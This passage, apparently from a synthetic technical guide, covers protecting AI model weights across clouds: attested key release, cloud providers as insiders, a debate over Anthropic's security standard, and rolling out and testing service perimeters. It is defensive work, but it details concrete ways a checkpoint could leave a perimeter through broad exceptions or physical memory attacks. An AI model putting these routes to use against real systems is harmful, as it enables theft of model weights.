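The transfer also needs an exception to the bandwidth limit. The checkpoint would take about ten months to transfer at the 0.3 megabits per second suggested earlier for the evaluation environment, but only 2 hours and 13 minutes at 1 gigabit per second. If the company opens the faster route for three hours, 1.35 TB could pass, which leaves room for three extra copies of model weights at RAND's planning size of 100 GB. A limit on total bytes is therefore safer than a time limit alone. Setting it at the file's size plus 1% leaves only 10 GB to spare.

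AWS DataSync can copy files from Google Cloud Storage, and Google's Storage Transfer Service can copy them from S3 or Azure. Both services pull data toward the destination, so the company has to let an identity in the serving cloud read the source. DataSync does this with a long-lived key, and anyone who steals the key may be able to fetch other checkpoints too. A program that pushes the file from the source needs only write permission at the destination, which an attacker on AWS can't use to read from Google Cloud.

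With the transfer service, anyone who wants to divert the file must change the program, impersonate it or get a harmful request past both approvers. This stops researchers and ordinary engineers, but a Google Cloud administrator can still give themselves access to the original, and an AWS administrator can do the same with the delivered copy.

### An encrypted copy and an outside key

Encryption can protect the delivered copy. A program in the training cloud generates a random 256-bit key, encrypts the checkpoint with it and sends only the encrypted file to AWS. The company then has to decide who can obtain the key.

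One option is external key management, in which the company keeps a master key on equipment outside the cloud that stores the data. AWS calls this an external key store, and Google calls it Cloud External Key Manager. The cloud usually encrypts each file with a data key and stores that data key in encrypted form. To open the file, the storage service sends a request to the provider's key service, which then sends a request to the company's equipment. If the request meets the company's rules, the equipment helps to decrypt the data key.

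This gives the company a record of each request to its equipment and lets it refuse all later ones. Google can also attach a reason to each request, such as a customer's own action or a support case, and the company can automatically reject requests with certain reasons. But the company has to trust Google to report the reason accurately.

The arrangement doesn't show what happens after the company's equipment approves a request. The data key and the decrypted file are then on the provider's machines, and anyone who copies them from there will still have the weights after the company switches off its master key. Any failure of the company's equipment also stops new serving machines from loading the model.

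### Releasing the key only to approved software

Attested key release adds a check on the machine that asks for the key. It relies on processors that encrypt a program's memory, so that the rest of the machine, including the provider's own control software, shouldn't be able to read it. The processor can also sign a report, called an attestation, about the software it started. For the example checkpoint, the process works like this:

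1. The company builds the serving software, reviews the code and records the hash of the finished image.
2. A serving machine on AWS starts the image in protected memory and creates a pair of keys, one public and one private.
3. The company's key service sends the machine a random number that it has never used before.
4. The machine returns a signed report that contains the random number, the software's hash, the firmware version and the machine's public key.
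5. The key service checks the signature, the random number and the firmware version. It also checks that debugging is off and that the hash is on the approved list.
6. If everything matches, it encrypts the checkpoint's key with the machine's public key. Only the program in protected memory has the private key that opens it.

The random number prevents a thief from reusing an old report. Putting the public key inside the report prevents him from attaching his own key to someone else's report.

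A valid report is good evidence that hardware the key service trusts started that exact software, but it doesn't show that the software is safe. If the approved image contains a debugging function that prints the weights, the machine passes every check and the function still works. The report also describes how the machine started, so it won't show if an attacker took over the program an hour later through a flaw in its code.

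Large models run mostly on accelerators, the specialized chips that do the arithmetic, so the report has to cover those chips too. Otherwise the weights leave protected memory as soon as the machine loads them onto an accelerator. Recent Nvidia chips can produce such reports, but support varies, so the company has to check each type of chip before relying on this design.

A chip maker may sign the attestation report, or the cloud provider may sign it, as AWS does for its Nitro Enclaves. If the provider signs it, the company is trusting the provider to describe its own machines. The company should also keep the key service outside the cloud that serves the model, so that no single provider runs the machine, checks the report and holds the key.

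To protect the key from a single administrator, the company can split it. The program in the training cloud picks a random value *K*₁ as long as the key *K* and calculates *K*₂ so that

*K* = *K*₁ ⊕ *K*₂,

where ⊕ compares the two values bit by bit and gives 1 wherever they differ. Either half alone reveals nothing about *K*. Two key services under different administrators each hold one half, and each checks the report before releasing it. The serving machine then depends on both services being available, which is a real cost when hundreds of machines restart at once.

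| Design | Who could divert usable weights | If an administrator in the training cloud is compromised | If an administrator in the serving cloud is compromised |
|---|---|---|---|
| Direct copy | Anyone who can use the sending machine or edit its route | He can read the original | He can read the delivered copy |
| Transfer service | Anyone who can change the program or use its identity | He can read the original | He can read the delivered copy |
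| Encrypted copy with attested release | Anyone who can get harmful software approved or break the hardware's protection | He can read the original | He gets only the encrypted file, if the hardware holds |

The company should combine the last two designs by having the transfer service send an encrypted copy. The original weights need separate protection under any design, because training requires them to be decrypted. The company could extend attested release to the training machines, but researchers change training code daily, and someone would have to approve each new version.

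### The provider as an insider

The provider's machines enforce every perimeter rule, so the rules can't restrain the people who control those machines. A provider employee might act alone, take a bribe or follow an executive's order. The company's options depend on what that employee can access.

| What the provider's employee does | What restrains him | What remains |
|---|---|---|
| Reads stored files | Encryption before upload, with the key held elsewhere | Decrypted weights on running machines |
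| Reads a machine's memory through the provider's control software | Protected memory | Flaws in the processor or firmware |
| Attaches equipment to the server | Guards, cameras and locked racks, all run by the provider | Employees who control the guards and cameras |
| Makes a false report about a machine | Reports signed by the chip maker | Signing keys that someone extracts from a chip |

The last two rows are more than theoretical. In October 2025, academic researchers published an attack called TEE.fail, which used equipment costing less than $1,000 to watch the traffic between a server's processor and its memory. They recovered secrets from protected memory on Intel and AMD processors, including keys that sign attestation reports. Someone with such a key can produce a valid report for an unprotected machine. The attack requires physical access to the server, which may be easy for a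 cloud provider's employees to get. Chip makers generally don't promise to withstand attacks that require such access.

Google and Microsoft also offer settings that let customers approve or deny support staff's access to their data. These are worth turning on to guard against a curious employee, but they do little against the provider itself, because the provider operates the approval step.

### Whether Anthropic's standard covers its cloud partners

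In late 2025, outside critics argued that Anthropic was probably violating its own security standard because employees of its cloud partners could reach the weights. The argument has four steps:

1. Anthropic's 2025 policy promised strong protection against several groups of attackers, including corporate espionage teams.
2. Amazon and Google host Claude in many regions, which suggests that the weights are in ordinary data centers. The critics drew the same conclusion about Microsoft.
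3. A senior executive at one of these companies could give an espionage team physical access to the machines and have someone alter the access records.
4. A competent team with unlimited physical access could extract the decrypted weights.

The critics cited an Anthropic paper on running models confidentially. It lists protections that data centers would need, many of which aren't standard practice. The critics thought such a theft improbable, but argued that the policy's promise covered classes of attacker, with no exception for those who lack a motive.

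#### The reply on scope

The policy left out "sophisticated" insiders, meaning people who have or can request access to systems that process weights. Anthropic staff first replied that this exclusion covers employees of cloud partners, who can be insiders on this reading.

The policy's wording supports the critics. The definition is in a footnote to the words "internal employees", and a separate clause on partners required Anthropic to document how models in a partner's environment would meet the same security criteria. One critic estimated that the wide reading would raise the number of insiders from 50–100 to 2,000–3,000. The policy also excluded about ten non-state groups that had state-level resources and could develop new attack methods. The largest cloud companies might fit that description, but an employee with a key to the server room may not need a new method.

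In the same discussion, an Anthropic employee narrowed the reading, saying he had meant only people with authorized access to the weights. He said the standard did cover a partner's employees who could touch the machines but lacked that authorization. This concedes much of the critics' point about wording but leaves open the factual question of whether those employees could get the weights out. His impression was that Anthropic was well protected against them, though he said he didn't know every detail of how it had vetted its partners.

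#### The reply on vetting

Anthropic's deputy security chief said the company applies its ASL-3 protections in every deployment environment, including clouds, with no exceptions for particular partners. He wouldn't discuss individual partnerships.

AWS says that its Nitro System, the hardware and software beneath its rented machines, gives no AWS employee a way to read customers' data. The security firm NCC Group reviewed the design and found no gaps that would undermine the claim. The review is good evidence that an administrator using AWS's normal tools can't read the data. It is weaker evidence that a team couldn't read it by opening the server and attaching its own equipment, and it doesn't cover Google or Microsoft.

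The defenders also said that a provider caught stealing from a customer would face criminal charges and lose other customers' trust. The threat of these consequences makes theft less likely but not impossible, and it depends on somebody detecting the theft.

The critics' evidence still doesn't justify the word "probably". They assumed that Anthropic gets roughly the same machines and terms as other customers, but a customer of its size may have negotiated dedicated hardware, its own cameras or stricter rules for entering the server rooms. Neither side has published the terms.

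#### What has changed since, and what would settle it

The 2025 policy is no longer in force, but the question remains open because Anthropic is still committed to its ASL-3 protections. According to ai.rud.is, the August 2026 Risk Report still treats corporate espionage as in scope and sophisticated insiders as out of scope. It also lists new computing capacity spread across providers with uneven security as one reason that protecting weights will get harder. In the 2025 policy, Anthropic said it would aim to clarify unintended ambiguities in the next update, but its summaries of revisions through May 2026 don't mention a new definition of an insider.

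In its July 2026 policy, Anthropic also recommends that once AI can automate research, developers should defend against the strongest plausible attackers not bound by a credible industry-wide safety regime. Companies under such a regime wouldn't need to treat each other as threats to their weights. Google hosts Anthropic's models and develops competing ones, so without such a regime it would count as a possible attacker.

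Four kinds of public evidence would go a long way toward deciding the matter:

- a definition that says which of a partner's employees count as insiders, with a rough number
- the documentation on partners' environments that the 2025 policy required, with sensitive details removed
- a statement of whether the serving machines, including their accelerators, use protected memory, and of who holds the keys
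- an independent test in which experts with physical access to a working server try to extract a harmless model, and report how long it took and what it cost

The test would be the most informative because it bears directly on the critics' fourth step. If a team succeeded with few resources, that would show that the standard wasn't met on that type of server, though a failed attempt wouldn't prove that the weights are safe from a better team.

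Anthropic's existing reviews might produce some of this. Under the July 2026 policy, external reviewers of a Risk Report see everything except what the law or Anthropic's legal rights require it to withhold, and they publish their disagreements. Anthropic has to commission such a review only when the report covers models that cross Anthropic's threshold for automated research and the public version omits important information, or when its oversight trust asks for one. A separate review, roughly once a year, checks whether Anthropic followed its procedures but doesn't judge how well the security works.

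Anthropic (2026) reported on October 19 that it had built a prototype of its key workflows and infrastructure under "extreme security practices". A prototype can show which protections are practical, but the dispute is about the machines that serve customers now.

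## Rolling out, testing and monitoring the perimeter

Enforcing every rule at once would probably interrupt training and serving, because nobody at the company knows every connection they depend on. The company should first run the rules without blocking anything, then enforce them in one environment at a time.

### The rollout order

1. Record real access. Switch on read logs for the weights bucket and use them to update the company's list of permitted transfers. Google Cloud recommends writing down who or what starts each one, under which conditions, and whether the company should allow it.
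2. Run the rules in a mode that records violations but blocks nothing. Have each team run all its jobs during this time, including rare ones such as restoring a backup.
3. Sort the violations into legitimate needs and unwanted transfers. Treat a violation that nobody can explain as unwanted.
4. Write a narrow exception for each legitimate need, and repeat the second step until only unwanted transfers remain.
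5. Enforce the rules on the evaluation environment.
6. Extend them to training, and finally to serving, where an outage would affect customers.

Evaluation is a good place to start because the researcher works there and an outage would only delay tests. On Google Cloud, the evaluation project has to share a perimeter with the weights bucket, so the engineer would enforce the perimeter on projects 101 and 103 first. Training and serving then need temporary ingress rules to use the bucket, and she deletes each project's rule when it joins the perimeter. On AWS, she can attach the service control policy (SCP) to the evaluation account alone. The resource control policy (RCP) on the weights bucket should come last, because a mistake in it would stop all three environments.

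A preview logs violations but does not block them. If the researcher copies the checkpoint to her personal bucket during the second step, the copy succeeds and the company has only a log entry. Microsoft warns that malicious actors may exploit resources left in Azure's preview mode. The company should set an end date for the preview and, until then, remove read access from everyone who can work without it. Rules that would not block any legitimate job, such as the ban on sharing snapshots, can take effect immediately.

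### Google's dry-run mode

A Google service perimeter can have an enforced configuration and a dry-run configuration. Google Cloud's *Dry run mode for service perimeters* explains that Google checks each request against the enforced one first. If the request passes but violates the dry-run configuration, Google logs the violation and lets the request through. This command, based on a sample in Native's *VPC Service Controls Explained*, creates a dry run for the weights perimeter, although the real list of services would be much longer:

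```
gcloud access-context-manager perimeters dry-run create weights \
  --perimeter-title="Weights" \
  --perimeter-resources=projects/101,projects/102,projects/103,projects/104 \
  --perimeter-restricted-services=storage.googleapis.com,compute.googleapis.com \
  --policy=222
```

Each log entry gives the service, the method, the project, the caller's email and IP address, and the reason for the violation. Some entries are harder to trace because Google hides the email when someone without permission tries to read something. It also records the IP address as `private` when the call came from one of its own services or from a network in a project outside the perimeter. One broken job can create thousands of entries, so the engineer should group them by identity, method and target.

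A dry run doesn't show the effects of switching the network to the restricted address range, so she has to check beforehand that every service the jobs use is available there. To test a change to an access level in a dry run, she has to copy the level and edit the copy.

Once someone has saved changes to a dry run, it also stops picking up changes to the enforced rules. Suppose an engineer saves a dry run in April, and in May a colleague removes a former partner from the enforced rules. The April version still includes the partner, so enforcing it in June would let the partner back in. The engineer should compare the two versions before enforcing the dry run. Google Cloud's *Manage dry run configurations* says that changes can take up to 30 minutes to take effect and that the perimeter might block requests in the meantime, so she shouldn't enforce the dry run just before a training run starts.

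### Previews on AWS and Azure

On AWS, the usual preview is to compare a proposed policy with past activity. AWS offers a free, open-source tool for this called the data perimeter helper. To preview the SCP that limits staff to company buckets, the tool works through these steps:

1. It searches the CloudTrail logs for S3 calls made by identities in one account.
2. It drops calls that failed, calls to buckets that the company owns or has listed as trusted, and calls by AWS services and service-linked roles, which SCPs don't restrict.
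3. It checks the remaining buckets against an inventory from AWS Config and drops any others that belong to the company.
4. It exports the rest as a report.

In AWS's example, the report shows that a role called `PartnerSync` has been using outside buckets, so the engineer asks its developers why. Another query lists outsiders who have permission to use the company's buckets, whether or not they have used it. The company can delete an unused permission instead of writing an exception for it.

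The tool can find only the S3 calls that CloudTrail recorded, and the company has to turn on that logging first. CloudTrail also doesn't record the values of condition keys, so the result is an estimate of what the policy would block. AWS's sample search covers seven days, which could miss a monthly transfer to a partner. Later reports omit any bucket on the trusted list, so additions to that list need the same review as exceptions.

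On Azure, transition mode provides the preview. The engineer should look for two log categories, `NspPublicInboundResourceRulesAllowed` and `NspPublicOutboundResourceRulesAllowed`, which record traffic that the resource's own settings allow but the perimeter's rules would refuse. Enforcement will block this traffic. Journey of the Geek found that Azure wrongly logged some permitted calls between members of a perimeter under a rule called `DenyAll`, so the engineer should check that a call needs an exception before writing one.

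### What commonly breaks

Build systems are a frequent problem. Google's Cloud Build runs its jobs on machines outside the perimeter even when the project that starts them is inside, so the builds lose access to protected resources. Package downloads also fail in Cloud Composer, which schedules data jobs, because it can't reach the public Python index from inside a perimeter, according to Native. On Azure, enforcing the perimeter ends the exemption for services that Microsoft treats as trusted.

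Troubleshooting tools may also stop working inside a perimeter. Google Cloud's *Deprecated VPC Service Controls support for Gemini Cloud Assist investigations* announced that from April 13, 2026, Google would block Investigations, an AI troubleshooting feature, inside perimeters because it might leak data.

An engineer who has to fix an outage quickly will tend to write a broad exception:

| What breaks | Hurried exception | What the researcher could then do | Narrower fix |
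|---|---|---|---|
| Software builds | Let the build account use every service in the weights perimeter | Start a build that reads the checkpoint on an outside machine | Let the account upload finished images and nothing else |
| Package downloads | Open the firewall to the internet | Upload the checkpoint to any website | Use the company's mirror |
| Web console | Admit the office network for Cloud Storage | Download the checkpoint to her laptop | Admit only calls that manage test machines |
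| Partner transfers | Let all staff write to the partner's project | Copy the checkpoint to a friend's bucket there | Admit only the program that sends scores |

Even published examples can be too broad to protect weights. Native's example of a narrow exception lets `ANY_SERVICE_ACCOUNT` read files in one project from the corporate network. If an engineer applied it to project 101, it would have the same weakness as the office-network exception in the table.

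### Measuring the exceptions

The company should calculate these measures every month. The limits are judgment calls and can be adjusted.

| Measure | How to calculate it | Suggested limit |
|---|---|---|
| Number | Count every rule, list entry, tag and exemption that lets a request past the perimeter | No increase without a new business need |
| Age | Days since someone last reviewed the exception | 90 days |
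| Owner | Share of exceptions with a named, current employee responsible for them | 100% |
| Breadth | Identities that can use the exception × destinations it opens | 1 for transfers to partners |
| Last use | Days since a request last needed the exception | 90 days, then delete it |

The rule for sending scores has a breadth of 1, because it lets one identity reach one project. If an engineer replaces that identity with a group of 40 researchers and adds a second partner's project, the breadth rises to 80, although it is still only one rule. An average would hide a rule like this, so the monthly report should give the largest breadth.

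The report should also count the exceptions that let an identity with read access to the weights send data outside the perimeter. The only such exception should be for the transfer service that moves weights between clouds.

### An acceptance test

The security team can test the perimeter with a marker file, such as 100 MB of random data, stored in the weights bucket with the same permissions as the checkpoint. The team also needs a Google Cloud project, an AWS account and an Azure tenant outside the company's organization. The identity used for the test should have the researcher's permissions, plus permission to write to storage in those outside accounts.

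Without that write permission, the copy would fail even if the perimeter were broken, so the team should first confirm the permission by uploading another harmless file from somewhere the perimeter rules don't apply. This can be a laptop for Google Cloud, or an equivalent role in a spare account that the SCP doesn't cover for AWS.

| Cloud | Transfer | Expected result | Expected log entry |
|---|---|---|---|
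| Google | Copy the marker to the outside bucket from a test machine | Fails | Policy Denied, with an egress violation naming the outside project |
| Google | Copy the marker to the sandbox | Fails | The same, naming project 202 |
| Google | Download the marker to a laptop | Fails | Policy Denied, with an ingress violation |
| AWS | Copy the marker to the outside bucket with work credentials | Fails | Access denied in the S3 data events, or `VpceAccessDenied` |
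| AWS | Upload the marker from a test machine with the outside account's credentials | Fails | `VpceAccessDenied` |
| AWS | Read the marker from home with an outside identity | Fails | Access denied in the S3 data events |
| AWS | Share a snapshot of a disk that holds the marker | Fails | A refused `ModifySnapshotAttribute` call |
| Azure | Download the marker at home | Fails | `NspPublicInboundPerimeterRulesDenied` |
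| Azure | Upload the marker from a test machine with the outside account's key | Fails | A blocked connection in the firewall log |
| All | Upload the marker to the security team's own web server | Fails | A blocked connection in the firewall log |
| All | Read the marker on a test machine | Succeeds | A read in the storage log, or `NspPrivateInboundAllowed` on Azure |
| All | Send a dummy score file to the partner | Succeeds | No denial, and the partner confirms that the file arrived |
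| All | Send a new software image to the evaluation environment | Succeeds | An upload in the registry's log |

After each attempt that should fail, the tester should also check that nothing arrived in the outside account. Google Cloud's command-line tool returns a unique ID with each refusal, and *Retrieve VPC Service Controls errors from audit logs* explains how to use that ID to find the matching log entry. The tester should wait at least 30 minutes after a rule change before testing, because temporary errors during that time could make a broken perimeter seem to work.

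In the first AWS row, both the SCP and the endpoint policy should block the copy, so the test still passes if one of them is broken. To test the SCP alone, the team can repeat the copy from a test network with an open endpoint policy. The second AWS row tests the endpoint policy alone, because the SCP doesn't apply to outside credentials.

Datadog, a monitoring vendor, describes similar tests of AWS's identity, resource and network perimeters that use an attack simulation tool called Stratus Red Team.

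A pass is good evidence that the perimeter blocked these calls, from these identities and networks, on that day. It provides little evidence about services the test didn't use, so the company also needs the coverage audit. A perimeter with the Bedrock flaw described earlier would have passed every row, because none of them calls Bedrock. The test also doesn't show whether an administrator could change the rules, or whether someone could slowly send out small pieces of the weights by a permitted route.

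The company should automate the test and run it daily and after every rule change. A weekly test would take three and a half days on average to find a newly broken rule.

### What the logs show

| Cloud | Denied crossings | Permitted crossings | Main blind spot |
|---|---|---|---|
| Google | Policy Denied audit logs | Each service's own access logs | The perimeter's log doesn't record use of an exception |
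| AWS | Network activity events with `VpceAccessDenied` | Network activity events, if the company logs all calls | Traffic that doesn't use an endpoint, and services without these events |
| Azure | Perimeter logs in the "denied" categories | Perimeter logs in the "allowed" categories | Uploads from machines, which can't join a perimeter |

Google Cloud's *VPC Service Controls audit logging* says customers can't switch off the Policy Denied logs but can exclude them from the default storage location. The company should therefore send a copy of these logs to its separate logging account.

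The company can see who uses its exceptions by keeping a dry-run version of the perimeter without them. Google logs requests that pass the enforced rules but violate the dry run, so each use of an exception should create a log entry. These entries also supply the "last use" measure. But the engineer has to add the exceptions back to the dry run before she can preview another change. If someone enforced the dry run without them by mistake, every transfer the exceptions allow would stop.

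On AWS, Wiz recommends logging at least the denied calls at every endpoint, which it says should be rare in a well-managed environment. For S3 in the weights unit, the company should also log permitted calls, because an upload that gets through a faulty endpoint policy would otherwise leave no network activity event.

Of the seven services permitted in the weights unit, AWS lists network activity events for only three (S3, KMS and EC2). The container registry, CloudWatch Logs, IAM and the Security Token Service (STS) are missing. Classmethod's *Trying Out the New "UserIdentity Filtering" Feature in CloudTrail Network Activity Events* found in July 2026 that STS events worked anyway, so the other three are worth testing. The same post shows that customers can now record events only for chosen identities. This saves money but could miss a thief who uses an unexpected identity, so the company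 shouldn't use it for the weights.

Azure's perimeter logs also record traffic through private endpoints, even though the perimeter doesn't restrict it. They would show the researcher reading from the storage account that holds the weights, but an analyst would need the firewall's logs to see an attempt to upload the file elsewhere. Azure may combine several events into one record, so an analyst counting events has to add up the `count` field instead of counting records.

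### Decoys

A decoy is a resource that no job uses, so any attempt to open it is suspicious. The company could create a bucket called `weights-backup` that contains only random data and set an alert for every read. The marker file can also serve as a decoy between tests.

Google Cloud suggests "honeypot perimeters" for detecting people who probe its services. A company can build one by putting a decoy project in a perimeter that has only a dry-run configuration. Google then logs requests from outside without refusing them, so the intruder gets no error that might warn them. Inventory and backup programs will also open decoys, so the company has to identify those programs before it can trust the alerts.

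Decoys work best against someone with stolen credentials who is still looking for the weights. The researcher already knows where the checkpoint is, so has no reason to open a decoy.

### Evidence from real deployments

There is little public evidence on how long a rollout takes, how much it breaks or how many exceptions remain. *Google Cloud adds VPC security tools for BlackLine* (Mitchell, 2026) reports that BlackLine, a financial software company, uses Google's perimeters to protect customer data. BlackLine says a new tool that explains blocked requests has significantly reduced the time it takes to resolve perimeter problems, but the article gives no figures for the time saved, outages or exceptions.

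On Azure, Journey of the Geek says enforced perimeters were until recently "pretty much a non-starter" for large companies, because they blocked logs from reaching a central workspace. This is one practitioner's judgment, but it fits the technical limits described earlier.

The company therefore has to estimate the time from its own preview. If the first full run of every job produces 60 distinct violations and the team can resolve 15 a week, the company needs at least four weeks, plus time to repeat the run, before it can enforce anything.
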